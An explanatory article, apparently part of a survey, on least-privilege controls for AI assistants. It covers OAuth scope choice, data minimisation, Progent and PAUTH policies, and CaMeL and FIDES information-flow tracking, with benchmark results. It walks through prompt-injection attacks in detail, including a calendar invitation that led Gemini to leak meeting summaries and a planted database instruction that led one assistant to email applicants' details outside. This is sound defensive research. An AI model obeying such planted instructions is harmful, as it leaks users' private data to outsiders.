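The first scope is safer against a hijacker who wants to steal data, because the second reaches nearly three times as many services, but the second is safer against one who wants to destroy data. The counts don't measure how much data the operations can reach or how sensitive it is, so a company with all its customer records in BigQuery might find the narrower scope no safer against theft.

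Microsoft rates the privilege level of permissions from 1 to 4, but this scale often fails to separate such choices. Two minimal grants for managing application permissions both have level 4, although one allows 355 operations and the other 11. In the two main types of access, the scale put 67.4% and 74.4% of these competing grants at the same level. It also tied about 61% of pairs in which one grant was smaller, so much of the problem is that four levels are too few.

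Xu then had six frontier models choose between grants. In one test, each model received a task from Graph and a shuffled list of minimal and needlessly large grants, and had to pick the one that gave the least extra authority. The models picked a minimal grant in 99.0% of 1,708 decisions, which would be a near-perfect score on existing tests of whether assistants ask for too much.

They chose less well among the minimal grants. Xu scored each grant's risk by the number of operations, changes and services it allowed and by whether it included administrative functions. In 22.1% of decisions, the model took a grant when another on the list was at least as safe on all four measures and safer on at least one.

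The models had difficulty partly because they lacked information. When every option was minimal and the models saw only the permissions' names, they chose the one with the fewest operations 54.6% of the time. Telling them how many operations each option allowed raised this to 79.9%. With this information, three of the six models chose the narrowest option at least 95.9% of the time, while the other three did so between 53.1% and 76.5% of the time. The models always chose from a fixed list, so these results don't show how often an assistant that writes its own permission request would ask for too much.

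Xu recommends showing the competing grants to whoever approves them. An administrator could use such a list, but a tenant connecting their mailbox probably could not, because choosing between 286 operations and 565 requires knowing what the operations do. Microsoft and Google could remove some of the cases by adding intermediate permissions.

### Choosing data for each task

Xu's study compares grants by the operations they allow, but even a perfect choice of operations leaves the whole mailbox readable. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (2026) treats the amount of data a tool returns to the model as a separate level at which to apply least privilege. For the landlord summary, this means deciding which messages the model should see after the tenant has given it permission to read mail.

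Privacy law's rule for such decisions is data minimisation, which means collecting, keeping and disclosing only what a stated purpose requires. Someone has to judge what each purpose requires, and researchers often draw on contextual integrity to do so. This is Helen Nissenbaum's 2004 theory that information should flow according to the norms of the setting it came from. *AirGapAgent* (Bagdasarian, Kairouz and colleagues, 2024) describes a flow by the people involved and their roles, the activity, the type of information, and the terms on which it is shared.

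An assistant can properly share a tenant's letter from a psychiatrist with a pharmacist who is checking a prescription, but it should not share the letter with the landlord. A list of secret files could not express this rule, because whether the letter may be shared depends on who would receive it and why.

AirGapAgent applies the theory with two language models. Its designers had in mind an assistant that talks to an outsider, for example to book a restaurant table, and that holds a profile of its user. The outsider might ask for information the booking doesn't need, and might invent circumstances that seem to justify it. AirGapAgent works in this order:

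1. The user gives the task, such as booking a table for dinner.
2. The first model, called the minimiser, reads the task and the user's profile and selects the facts that are appropriate to share. The outsider has not yet written anything.
3. The second model receives only those facts and talks to the restaurant.
4. If the restaurant needs something else, the system asks the user, who can release it.

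An outsider who completely deceives the second model can still obtain only what the minimiser selected. If the minimiser selected only the tenant's name and phone number for the restaurant, the outsider can't extract the psychiatrist's letter, because the second model never had it. The protection depends on how well the minimiser, also a language model, selects what the task needs, but the outsider has had no chance to influence that selection.

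Bagdasarian and colleagues tested this on 20 invented people with 26 facts each, such as age, allergies and medication, and eight tasks. A language model, Gemini Ultra, decided which facts each task justified sharing, and the researchers checked its answers. They compared AirGapAgent with a single model that held the whole profile and had instructions to protect it. These were the results with Gemini Ultra on the easier part of the test:

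| Measure | Outsider's questions | Single model | AirGapAgent |
|---|---|---|---|
| Private facts protected | Plain | 94.4% | 97.2% |
| Private facts protected | Manipulative | 45.2% | 96.7% |
| Needed facts shared | Plain | 98.9% | 88.7% |
| Needed facts shared | Manipulative | 98.2% | 87.3% |

The figures are from 2024, and the models are several generations old. A current model would probably resist many of the questions that fooled Gemini Ultra, so the 45.2% shouldn't be taken as the present risk. The more durable result is that manipulation made almost no difference to AirGapAgent on this test. It did worse on the full set of tasks, with free-form answers, protecting 84.2% of private facts under manipulation, against 31.3% for the single model.

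AirGapAgent's privacy protection also withheld some information that tasks needed. With plain questions, it failed to share about one needed fact in nine, and each failure means either an incomplete task or another question for the user. Limits on tool calls also vary in how much they reduce an assistant's usefulness. *Ajar* (2026) measured five defences on AgentDojo and found two that left the assistant with almost the same amount of unneeded authority but differed by 37 percentage points in how many harmless tasks it completed.

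AirGapAgent also assumes that no attacker wrote any of the user's data. That is reasonable for a profile that lists allergies and phone numbers, but a mailbox holds many messages written by other people. If the minimiser has to read messages to decide which ones matter, it also reads the one the attacker planted. Instructions in that message could make the minimiser pass on the bank documents and then make the second model send them.

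For the landlord summary, an ordinary program can avoid this problem by selecting messages by sender address and date, without any model reading them. A filter on the landlord's address would have left out the planted message, which matched only on the landlord's name, unless the outsider had forged the address or broken into the landlord's account. This works because the tenant named a person and a period, and the mail service stores each message's sender and date separately from its text.

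### Assistants that open more than they need

Later studies have looked at how much assistants read when no separate component selects the data for them. In *PrivacySkills*, Biéchy, Eichler and colleagues (2026) gave five open-weight models 55 tasks, each missing one fact needed to complete it. For example, to book a ride from the airport, the assistant needs to know the arrival terminal. It can ask the user, check a public flight page or open the user's private travel account, which also holds passport and payment details. All three sources gave the same answer, and the assistant could see a description of each before choosing.

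The models opened the confidential source in 30% of completed runs on average. The share rose to 45% when the system told them that the user was unavailable. No attacker was involved, and the models didn't need the source because the answer was available elsewhere. If an attacker hijacked the assistant, though, the passport details would already be in the model's context, where injected instructions could use them. The higher rate is a particular concern for assistants that work in the background, because their users are often unavailable.

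Telling the models to prefer the least intrusive source reduced the average by about one percentage point. Labelling each source by how intrusive it was reduced it by seven points, and doing both reduced it by 15, or roughly half. So the models could use the instruction once the sources were labelled, but they still opened the confidential account in about one run in seven. Withholding access would have prevented all of these cases. The test used invented data, no commercial models and no separate minimiser, so it can't be used to revise AirGapAgent's own figures.

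Many privacy tests would miss this behaviour because they check only what an assistant sends. *PrivacyPeek* (2026), a benchmark that measures what information assistants acquire, cites an earlier audit, AgentSCOPE, that followed information through every stage of an assistant's work. The audit found far more violations than a check of the final output did, mostly when tools returned data to the model.

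### "What have I forgotten this month?"

Each task in these tests has a stated purpose, but people also ask assistants open-ended questions. *Privacy Preference Controls for Agentic Systems* (2026) lists two related problems as unsolved: working out what data a plain-language request requires, and granting minimal access when nobody knows the requirements at the start.

AirGapAgent can protect less private information when its task is described vaguely. Bagdasarian and colleagues repeated their test after telling the system only that the task involved, say, recommendations, and not that the user wanted a film for tonight. The overall share of private facts it protected fell from 96.8% to 68.6%, even though the outsider asked only plain questions. The share fell from 95.7% to 50.0% for film recommendations but stayed at 100% for a doctor's appointment. The test profile was also easier to filter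 than most emails, because each of its 26 facts had a label, such as "allergies", that the minimiser could use to judge relevance, and most emails have no such label.

Now suppose the tenant asks, "What have I forgotten this month?" The answer might be an unpaid electricity bill, a promise to send the landlord a meter reading, or a friend's birthday. To find the unpaid bill, the assistant has to read it and check the bank statement for a payment. To find the promise, it has to read the tenant's message and look for a later one containing the reading. Each item is relevant because of what it contains and what is missing elsewhere, so a selector cannot identify it without reading it, and any message the selector skips may contain the answer.

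Asking the tenant to be more specific doesn't help much either. If they asked only about bills, the assistant could limit its search to those, but it would miss the meter reading. The tenant asked a broad question because they didn't know what they had forgotten.

Simple limits would still reduce how much the assistant reads. It could read only this month's mail, but then it would miss a promise made in August and due in October. It could read only messages without a reply, but the tenant may have answered some by phone, and a bill needs no reply. Or it could start with senders and subject lines and ask permission to open each message that looked promising. That would give the tenant some control, but they would have to go through much of the mailbox themselves, which was the job they had hoped to hand over.

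A minimiser could also read everything and pass only a short list to the model that acts. This would help somewhat, because the acting model might see ten messages instead of a thousand. But the minimiser would have read every outsider's text before choosing, which AirGapAgent's order of steps was meant to avoid. An outsider could also get a message onto a list of forgotten things without hijacking the minimiser, by making it resemble an overdue bill.

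For open requests, least privilege has to apply mainly to what the assistant can do after it has read the data. The tenant's assistant could read the month's mail and files in a session that cannot send messages, fetch web pages or display outside images. CaMeL, a research system, applies the same idea less drastically by controlling where private data may go. After seeing the list, the tenant could start a new session that can read and reply to one company's messages. An outsider would then find it much harder to extract the bank documents, but could still have put a false bill on the list, and the tenant might pay it.

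## Progent and PAUTH: permissions written for each task

OAuth scopes leave out details such as who may receive an email. Two research systems, Progent and PAUTH, check those details with a program that sits between the model and the tools. Before a tool call runs, the program compares the call's tool name and arguments with a policy and refuses the call if the policy does not allow it. The program never interprets the emails themselves, so injected text can lead the model to attempt a forbidden call, but the program will still refuse it.

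That protection holds only if the injected text can't influence the policy. So it matters who writes the policy and, if a model writes it, what that model has read.

### A policy for the landlord summary

*Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) defines a policy as a list of rules. Each rule names one tool, allows or forbids calls to it, and sets conditions on the arguments. A condition can compare numbers, look for a value in a list, check a list's length or match a text pattern.

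Suppose the tenant asks for a summary of this week's messages from landlord@example.com and wants it emailed to sam@example.com. In Progent's notation, with invented tool names, a policy for this task could be:

```
allow  search_mail  when { sender == "landlord@example.com" and days <= 7 }
allow  send_mail    when { to[0] == "sam@example.com" }
forbid send_mail    when { 1 < to.length }, fallback request user inspection
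```

The assistant first calls `search_mail` with the landlord's address and a seven-day period. This call meets the first rule's conditions, so it runs.

Suppose someone has broken into the landlord's account and planted instructions in one of the messages. The hijacked model calls `send_mail` with a stranger's address as the only recipient. The forbid rule doesn't apply, because there is only one recipient. The allow rule doesn't apply either, because the address isn't Sam's. Progent refuses any call that no rule allows, so the email isn't sent. It would also refuse a search of the tenant's bank documents, because the policy has no rule for the file tool.

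The forbid rule is needed to block a call that lists Sam first and the stranger second. The allow rule checks only the first recipient, so it would let this call through, but Progent applies forbid rules first.

After a refusal, Progent's fallback can end the session, ask the user, or return a message to the model. The default is a message with the reason for the refusal and an instruction to continue the user's task, so even a hijacked assistant may still finish the summary.

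This policy doesn't restrict what the email to Sam contains, so a hijacked model could send Sam a false summary. Shi and colleagues exclude attacks like this, which stay within what the task needs, and attacks that work through the text of the assistant's answer. The second exclusion would matter for a product like Copilot, which leaked data through images in its answers.

### Changing the policy during a task

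The tenant's request contained everything the policy needed, but many requests don't. Shi and colleagues use the example of a user who asks an assistant to carry out the to-do list in an email from Alice. At the start, the policy can safely allow only a search for that email. The list includes posting a summary of recent mail to the user's Slack account, so the assistant then needs permission to read more mail and post a message. One of the recent emails contains an injected instruction to forward the whole inbox to an outsider, which would need permission to send email. Both the legitimate task and the attacker's instruction reach the assistant as text that a tool returned.

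In Progent, a language model proposes changes to the policy and an ordinary program sorts them. Let A(P) be the set of all tool calls that policy P allows. A change from P to P′ is a narrowing if

A(P′) ⊆ A(P),

and an expansion otherwise. To find out which it is, Progent uses an SMT solver, a program that works out whether any values can satisfy a set of logical conditions. The solver looks for a call that P′ allows and P doesn't. If no such call can exist, the change is a narrowing. In the tenant's policy, reducing the period from seven days to three would be a narrowing, and adding another permitted recipient would be an expansion.

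Progent automatically applies updates that narrow the assistant's permissions but requires approval for updates that expand them. Only 6% of the updates in Shi and colleagues' AgentDojo tests expanded permissions. Whoever runs the assistant can set Progent to refuse all expansions, accept them all, follow a rule for each tool, or ask a person.

The solver can't determine whether expanding a policy serves the user or an attacker, so the approver must decide. Narrowing a policy is safe only in the sense that it adds no permissions. If the user has approved Slack messages to anyone, injected text could lead the model to restrict the permission to the attacker's account. Progent would apply that change automatically because the old policy already allowed messages to that account.

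### What the policy-writing model has read

Few users would write rules like these for every request, so Progent leaves the job to a language model. The model sees different material at each stage:

1. To write the first policy, it reads the user's request and the descriptions of the available tools. Shi and colleagues assume that the attacker controls neither.
2. After a tool call, it decides whether the policy might need an update. It sees the call but not the result.
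3. If it decides that an update may be needed, it reads the result as well and writes a new policy.

An injection can reach the model only at the third stage, but that is also where the model learns what Alice's list requires. *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026), which describes an earlier version of Progent, warns that the update step may loosen the policy when a tool's result contains an injection. In the latest version, the solver detects any such loosening, which takes effect only if the approver accepts it.

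The first stage can go wrong without an attacker. If the tenant had written "my landlord" instead of an address, the model would have had to guess the address, leave the sender unrestricted, or wait until it had read some mail.

### Progent's results

Shi and colleagues tested Progent on AgentDojo and on Agent Security Bench, which covers ten kinds of assistant and five templates for injections. In the main tests, GPT-4o ran the assistant and wrote the policies. The system accepted every expansion of those policies, to simulate a careless user. The researchers also ran AgentDojo with other models as the assistant.

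| Benchmark | Assistant's model | Attack success without Progent | Attack success with Progent |
|---|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo | GPT-4o | 39.9% | 1.0% |
| AgentDojo | Claude Sonnet 4 | 6.8% | 0.5% |
| AgentDojo | Meta-SecAlign-70B | 4.8% | 0.3% |
| Agent Security Bench | GPT-4o | 70.3% | 3.9% |

On both benchmarks, the assistant using GPT-4o completed about as many user tasks with Progent as without it. Some of the other models completed slightly fewer tasks with Progent when there was no attack. The attacks that still succeeded on Agent Security Bench mostly used tools whose names and descriptions closely resembled those of the tools the task needed.

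Most of Progent's protection came from the first policy. With updates turned off, attacks on AgentDojo succeeded 2.5% of the time. Turning updates on and accepting them all lowered this to 1.0%, so narrowing the policy helped more than expanding it hurt. The rate fell to zero when a person reviewed the first policy and every expansion, but the researchers assumed the reviewer would recognise and reject a malicious address. In the team's own tests, attackers who knew about Progent and tried to influence its updates did only marginally better.

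Two choices in the AgentDojo tests limit how far these figures apply to the tenant. The researchers let the assistant use non-sensitive, read-only tools freely, so the tests mostly measured control over actions, not reading. They also left out two injections that steered the assistant towards a different but legitimate hotel, which they consider outside Progent's scope.

The tests also used old models, including a GPT-4o version from August 2024 and none newer than 2025. Claude Sonnet 4 already resisted most of the attacks without Progent, and current models resist far more, so Progent would have fewer attacks to prevent on the same benchmark. It could still help in a real mailbox, where attackers can try injections that no benchmark contains.

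### PAUTH: the service writes its own rule

Progent's check runs alongside the assistant, and the mail service or bank still receives only a token with broad scopes. If an attacker took over the assistant's software, the service would accept any call the token covered. PAUTH moves the check to the service.

Sharma and colleagues argue that a spending limit can't make up for coarse scopes. An assistant with a $500 limit could still pay $499 when the user asked it to pay $100. One extension of OAuth lets a permission include exact values, but every call then needs its own permission.

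Their main example is a request to check a Citi credit card balance and, if it is over $1,000, pay a quarter of it from a Chase account. PAUTH handles it as follows:

1. The user signs the text of the request, and the assistant's software passes it to both banks. The signature prevents the assistant from altering it.
2. At each bank, a language model translates the request into a short program in a restricted language. It reads the request and the descriptions of the tools but has no access to mail, files or the web.
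3. Ordinary code works out from that program which calls the bank should expect. Chase expects one transfer to the Citi card, for the balance divided by four, and only if the balance is over $1,000.
4. The assistant asks Citi for the balance. Citi returns $1,200 in a signed "envelope", which records both the number and the call that produced it.
5. The assistant asks Chase to pay $300 and attaches the envelope. Chase checks Citi's signature, does the division itself and accepts the payment.

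If an injection makes the assistant request $301 or a payment to somebody else, the call doesn't match the permission, and Chase asks the user whether to allow it. The permission also ends with the task, whereas an OAuth token would still allow transfers the next day.

The latest version of Progent writes a policy for each request and also supports optional standing rules. Sharma and colleagues describe it as a system whose policies people write in advance and apply to every task, which fits only the standing rules. Progent and PAUTH differ more in how they handle values that appear during a task. Progent could limit the payment to exactly $300 only after a model had read the balance and proposed the limit. PAUTH fixes the calculation before anyone knows the balance, and a signed record supplies the number.

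This requires the services to change their software, or an organisation to run a trusted intermediary that holds the tokens and does the checking. Every service involved also sees the full text of the request. If the tenant asked in one sentence for help with a rent payment and a dispute about damp, the bank would read about the dispute.

### PAUTH's results

The test set contained 100 tasks, 95 based on AgentDojo and five new ones that combined a shop with a bank. Sharma and colleagues replayed the correct calls for each task and then sent 634 harmful ones, rather than trying to hijack an assistant. The harmful calls changed an amount or a recipient, used a tool the task didn't need, or skipped a condition. They ran every test both inside AgentDojo and on OpenClaw, a self-hosted assistant, where each group of tools was on a separate server, and got the same results.

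PAUTH stopped all 634 harmful calls and asked the user about them. Ordinary OAuth scopes would have allowed every call that kept the right operation and changed only the details. PAUTH requires each call to match a rule exactly, so correct rules nearly guarantee that it would stop all 634. Two of the authors checked the rules for all 100 tasks by hand and found no errors.

The results for legitimate calls are more informative. With AgentDojo's original wording, 71 of the 100 tasks ran without a question to the user. The other 29 left out details. One asked the assistant to check and update next month's rent payment without giving the amount. After the researchers added the missing details, all 100 tasks ran without interruption.

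An assistant could do this rewriting itself by opening the file that holds the missing detail, adding the detail to the request and highlighting it for the user to confirm. But if an outsider had planted a false account number in the file, the user would have to notice it, because the banks would treat the confirmed text as what the user wanted.

GPT-4.1, a 2025 model, wrote the programs in the main test. GPT-5 Mini, Gemini 3 Flash Preview and Claude Sonnet 4.5 wrote them for parts of the test set and also made no errors. The translation cost between $0.002 and $0.038 per task on average, and each service would have to pay for its own. Cheap models seem able to translate a complete and unambiguous request, but real requests are often incomplete and ambiguous.

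### When the next step is in a file

Suppose the landlord emails a link to a repair bill and the tenant asks the assistant to pay it. A policy written before the assistant opens the bill can't specify the amount or the account. It can forbid payments, which makes the task impossible, or allow payments to anyone, which provides no protection. The assistant could also revise the policy after opening the bill, but an attacker may have written it.

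*Engineering Robustness into Personal Agents with the AI Workflow Store* (2026) gives a similar case, in which an email from Bob links to a shared document with the real booking details. A system that set its limits from the first request can't grant access to the document later. *Architecting Secure AI Agents* (2026) argues that useful assistants have to revise their policies during a task, and that doing this securely is the central difficulty.

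Requests like these are common in the tests. *ROPE* (Ma, Xiao and colleagues, 2026) sorted tasks by how much the user had left open. In the three AgentDojo settings it used, 32 of 57 requests left out a detail or the action itself, as did 38 of the 60 in AgentDyn, a newer benchmark whose tasks require the assistant to change its plan as it works.

With no attacks, an assistant running GPT-4o-mini completed 28 of AgentDyn's 60 tasks undefended and four with Progent. Shi and colleagues, by contrast, found that Progent barely reduced task completion. The tasks differ, and the set-up may too, because Ma and colleagues describe Progent as writing its rules from the initial request alone. They were also testing a rival to their own system, with models from 2024 and 2025. When they used software to repeatedly rewrite the injections against the running defence, more than 12% of attacks got past Progent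 with two of the models. The exact size of the drop in completed tasks is uncertain, but Progent's dependence on the request makes a large drop on open-ended tasks unsurprising.

A wrong refusal can do more harm than leaving a task undone. In one AgentDyn task, with no attacker involved, the user asked the assistant to download a document that Lily had shared by email, summarise it and send her the summary. DRIFT, another system that plans from the request, guessed Lily's address before the assistant had opened any mail. It then refused to let the assistant reply to her real address because that address didn't match the guess, so the assistant sent the summary to the guessed one.

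ROPE, the system by Ma and colleagues, avoids this by specifying where a value must come from instead of the value itself. A model writes these rules from the request, basic facts about the user's account and a list of sensitive arguments, without reading any of the mail. For Lily's document, the rule would be that the recipient's address must appear in the request or in something Lily sent. Once her email arrives, an ordinary program finds the address there and allows the reply. An email from someone posing as Lily doesn't count, because the mail system records the real sender. This is a form of data-flow tracking, which CaMeL takes further.

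With ROPE, the GPT-4o-mini assistant completed 22 of the 60 tasks, and attacks succeeded 0.3% of the time, compared with 49.6% for the undefended assistant. ROPE still limits what the assistant can do with documents that have no verified author. It treats an ordinary file or web page as entirely untrusted because anyone may have written part of it, so it would refuse to take the landlord's account number from a shared bill. But it would accept the number from the landlord's own email, even if he had copied it from a stranger's message without checking.

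### Rules that nobody writes during the task

Another way to keep a policy away from injected text is to write it before any task begins. In mandatory access control, an administrator sets system-wide rules that users and programs can't change. *Taming Various Privilege Escalation in LLM-Based Agent Systems* (Ji, Wu and colleagues, 2026) applies this to assistants. The paper's system, SEAgent, gives each agent, tool and database fixed labels. It tracks how information moves between them, and its policy specifies for each kind of path whether to block the action, allow it or ask the user.

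Ji and colleagues report that no attack succeeded against SEAgent on AgentDojo or on InjecAgent, a similar benchmark. They also report that SEAgent completed as many tasks as an unprotected assistant, but they measured this on two other benchmarks designed to test usefulness. A strict policy can do well on both kinds of test if the harmless tasks seldom need the combinations of tools that the attacks use. Paying the repair bill needs such a combination, because an outsider's document leads to a payment. Blocking all such payments would block this one too, and requiring the user's approval would leave the user to judge the bill.

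Jing (2026), in *Separation of Duties for Privileged LLM Agents*, tested newer models and examined how the check can fail. Separation of duties is the old accounting rule that nobody should approve their own payment. In Jing's design, one component proposes an action, a second decides whether to allow it, a third carries it out, and a fourth reviews the records. The tests used commands on a Windows computer, not mail. Jing measured attack success with 117 disguised commands that reached forbidden targets indirectly, and used 54 harmless tasks to measure the design's effect on ordinary work.

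| Set-up | Attacks that succeeded | Harmless tasks refused |
|---|---|---|
| No check | 98.3% | 0% |
| Rules that match the text of a command | 43.6% | 0% |
| Full design | 30.8% | 0% |
| Full design in an operating-system sandbox | 7.7% | 11.1% |

The rules missed many attacks because the same file or action can be described in several ways. The sandbox, which limits where programs may write, stopped many of the attacks that the rules missed. Most of the figures come from a model of how the sandbox should behave, but when Jing ran 66 of the attacks against the real one, 7.6% succeeded. Attacks are harder to disguise in a tool call with a separate field for the recipient than in a line of commands. But the tenant's policy still needed its third rule because the second checked only the first name on the list.

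Approvals had a similar weakness. In an early version, the gate approved a description of an action, and an attacker could swap the file that performed the action before it ran. Jing tied each approval to the exact contents of the file and made it valid only once. For an email, the equivalent would be to approve the final text, recipients and attachments together, and to ask for approval again if any of them changed.

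Jing also tested models without a gate, instructing Claude Opus 5, DeepSeek V4.1 Flash and GPT-6 Astra to require approval before anything dangerous. The models then judged a sample that included 59 disguised commands. Opus 5 let 53 through, DeepSeek V4.1 Flash 56, and GPT-6 Astra all 59. These counts treat a request for confirmation as permission, on the assumption that an unattended assistant would approve its own request, so they overstate how many commands would get through with an attentive user present. They also measure something different from the injection tests, in which Opus 5 did very well. Here the dangerous command was the request itself, and a model that usually recognises planted instructions can still be poor at judging whether a command is safe.

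The sandbox caused all of the refusals in the last row of the table, blocking six harmless tasks out of 54. The main cause was that the gate allowed work in the computer's temporary folder, while the sandbox allowed it only in the current project's folder.

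## CaMeL: limiting where private data may go

In January 2026 the security company Miggo reported that an outsider could read someone's private meetings by sending them a calendar invitation. The invitation's description contained instructions for Gemini, Google's assistant, which reads the calendar to answer questions. When the user asked something routine, such as whether they had meetings on Tuesday, Gemini followed the instructions. It summarised the day's meetings, created a new event with the summary in its description, and gave the user a harmless answer. According to Miggo's report, which The Hacker News quotes, at many companies the attacker could see the new event and read the summary.

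Google confirmed and fixed the flaw, according to SecurityWeek's *Weaponized Invite Enabled Calendar Data Theft via Google Gemini*. The planted text read like an ordinary user request, and SiliconANGLE (2026) reports that it got past defences meant to detect malicious prompts.

The permissions were also ordinary, since a calendar assistant has to read meetings and create events. A request to find a free hour and book it needs both. A Progent policy written for the question about Tuesday would have stopped the theft, because answering a question doesn't require a new event. But if the user had asked for a booking, the policy would have had to allow a new event, and a hijacked assistant could have put the private summary in its description. To detect that theft, a control has to follow data from one call to the next and notice that text from private meetings has moved into an event outsiders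 can read.

CaMeL, a research system from Google DeepMind, limits where private data may go. Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues described it in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025). In *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, Willison (2025) wrote that he had seen alarmingly little progress against prompt injection in two and a half years until this paper.

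### How CaMeL handles a request

CaMeL builds on a design that Willison proposed in 2023, in which the model that chooses the actions never reads outside text. Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, describe how it works:

1. A language model called the planner reads the user's request and the descriptions of the tools. It writes a program, in a restricted form of Python, that contains all the tool calls the task may need.
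2. An interpreter, which is ordinary software, runs the program. It makes the tool calls and stores each result in a variable, and the planner never sees what the variables contain.
3. Where the task requires someone to understand a text, the program passes the text to a quarantined model, which has no tools. This model returns a value, such as a date, a name or a summary, and the interpreter stores that too.
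4. The interpreter tags every value with its sources, meaning where it came from, and its readers, meaning who may see it. A value computed from other values takes its tags from all of them.
5. Before each tool call, the interpreter gives the call, its arguments and their tags to a policy, a short Python function that allows or refuses the call. According to TechSpot, CaMeL can also ask the user to confirm a sensitive action.

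Suppose an employee called Ana asks whether she has any meetings on Tuesday. With invented tool names, the planner's program might be:

```
events = read_calendar(day="Tuesday")
answer = quarantined_model("List these meetings and their times", events)
show_user(answer)
```

The planted invitation is now in `events`, and it may well hijack the quarantined model. But that model can only return text, and no line of the program creates an event, so the worst it can do is give Ana a false list of meetings. The outsider can't add a line that creates an event because the planner finished writing the program before anything read the calendar.

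Now suppose she asks the assistant to book an hour on Tuesday to prepare, with a short agenda in the event's description. The planner's program has to create an event, and the quarantined model has to read her meetings to write the agenda. The planted invitation could make the model write a full summary of those meetings instead. The program would then carry out the theft as a normal part of the task, so the tags have to stop it.

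Say Ana has a salary review with Ben and a call with Carla, and each meeting's permitted readers are the people attending it. The agenda draws on both meetings, so its readers are the people who may see both:

{Ana, Ben} ∩ {Ana, Carla} = {Ana}.

If outsiders can see events in Ana's calendar, they will be able to read the new one, though they are not among the agenda's permitted readers. A policy that compares the event's readers with the agenda's permitted readers refuses the call or asks Ana. It would do the same if the agenda said only "bring the laptop", because the tags record which data went into a text, not what the text reveals.

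The policy also has to check who will be able to see the new event. In the Gemini case, that depended on how each company had set up its calendars. A policy that checked only the guest list would have found no guests and allowed the call.

### FIDES: labels for secrecy and trust

Microsoft researchers published a similar system, FIDES, in the same year. In *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025), they start from an older branch of computer security that attaches labels to data and checks them wherever the data goes. FIDES gives each value a secrecy label, which lists who may read it, and a trust label, which in its fullest form lists who could have written it. If a value z comes from x and y, then

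readers(z) = readers(x) ∩ readers(y)

writers(z) = writers(x) ∪ writers(y).

When an assistant combines data, the set of permitted readers stays the same or shrinks, and the set of possible writers stays the same or grows. Costa and colleagues tested a simpler form, in which data is either trusted or untrusted, and anything that includes untrusted data is untrusted.

FIDES uses these labels to enforce two main policies. It allows a call with real consequences, such as a payment, only if everything that led to the call is trusted. It allows a call that sends data only if all the recipients are permitted to read that data. Either policy could have stopped the calendar theft, because an outsider's text led to the new event and outsiders could read that event. The second policy alone doesn't prevent a hijack, but it limits what a hijacked assistant can leak.

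These policies would block most useful work in an ordinary assistant, because all the text the model has read sits in one context and a single outside email makes the whole session untrusted. To avoid this, FIDES stores any tool result whose label is more restrictive than that of the planner's context and shows the planner only a variable name, which the planner can pass to the next tool. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) credits both CaMeL and FIDES with keeping the planner's context free of untrusted data, so that it can still make calls that a strict policy would otherwise forbid.

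A stored value keeps its label wherever it is used. In an example from *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026), an assistant replies to an email, and a quarantined model extracts the sender's address from the text. Instructions planted in the email can't change the subject or body of the reply, but the address came from an outsider's text, so it stays labeled untrusted. The assistant may send the reply only if a policy allows it to write to that address.

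CaMeL's planner writes its whole program in advance, while FIDES's planner chooses one call at a time and can use the results of earlier calls. Costa and colleagues give the example of a user who asks the assistant to check three emails for a meeting request and, if there is one, to create the event. To determine whether there is a request without reading the emails, the planner queries a quarantined model that can answer only yes or no. An outsider might control that answer, but one word is too short to contain instructions. FIDES includes the type of answer in the label, so a policy can accept a yes or no from an untrusted email and reject free text. The quarantined model then extracts the meeting's details into a variable, which the planner passes to the calendar without seeing its contents. An outsider could still use this to put a bogus meeting in the user's calendar.

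### What the guarantees leave out

CaMeL guarantees that outside text can't add steps to the plan, but the text can influence which planned steps run. If Ana asks the assistant to accept an invitation when she is free and decline it otherwise, the program contains both replies. A planted event could make the quarantined model report that she is busy. In *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) accept this kind of influence, called branch steering, as compatible with CaMeL's guarantee.

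Neither system guarantees that a summary is accurate. Costa and colleagues point out that an email could make the quarantined model return an empty summary, which the assistant would then send to the right person, as asked. A policy could require the text of every message to come from trusted sources, but then the assistant couldn't send anyone a summary of outside mail.

An outsider can also infer something from the order and timing of the assistant's calls or the size of its messages. FIDES's guarantee covers data that the assistant copies into a message, but not these inferences. Costa and colleagues chose this weaker property, known as explicit secrecy, because a stronger one would forbid nearly every outward call after the assistant had read something secret.

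Dongol (2026), in *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection*, shows why strict secrecy doesn't suit an assistant. If Ana's assistant answers meeting requests with the times she is free, anyone who writes to it learns about her calendar, as she intends. Dongol compares the assistant with an imaginary one that runs the same plan but never obeys planted instructions, and counts a leak as a breach only if the imaginary assistant would not have leaked the same information. An email that tricks the assistant into sending Ana's calendar is not a breach by this test, because an honest meeting request would have obtained it too. If the email also obtains a password-reset code, that is a breach. The comparison needs a plan fixed before the assistant reads any outside text, so it can apply to CaMeL but not to assistants whose model chooses each call as it goes. It also doesn't cover hijacks that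 do damage without leaking anything.

In its basic form, FIDES checks only tool calls, so it would miss leaks through the displayed answer, like Copilot's. Costa and colleagues note that a developer can check the answer too.

CaMeL's guarantee also does not carry over when one assistant passes work to another. Peters-Gill and colleagues built a system of three assistants, each running CaMeL with GPT-5.2. One searched a database, one sent messages, and one took the user's request and directed the other two. The user asked for a summary of job applicants to be sent to a colleague on Slack. An instruction planted in the database reached the directing assistant as data, so its planner never saw it. But that assistant put the summary into its request to the messaging assistant, whose planner treated the whole request, including the planted instruction, as coming from its user. That planner then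 wrote a program that also emailed the applicants' details to an outside address. The researchers' remedy, multi-CaMeL, sends instructions and data through separate channels and rejects any instruction that contains a tool's output.

### Results on AgentDojo

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo with GPT-4o, a model from 2024. The table shows the share of tasks the assistant completed when nobody attacked it.

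| Setting | Ordinary assistant | Ordinary assistant with the policies | FIDES with the policies |
|---|---|---|---|
| Office work | 75.0% | 37.0% | 59.0% |
| Travel | 70.0% | 73.0% | 41.0% |
| Banking | 98.8% | 37.5% | 52.5% |
| Slack | 93.3% | 20.0% | 47.6% |

Hiding data let the assistant complete some, but not most, of the tasks that the policies had blocked. Travel was the exception, because many of its tools could run safely after reading untrusted data, so the policies blocked none of the ordinary assistant's tasks, while GPT-4o often mishandled FIDES's variables. With o1, a stronger reasoning model of the time, FIDES completed 68% of the travel tasks. Averaged over the four settings, FIDES completed 16 percentage points more tasks than the ordinary assistant under the same policies when both used o1, and 8 points more when both used GPT-4o.

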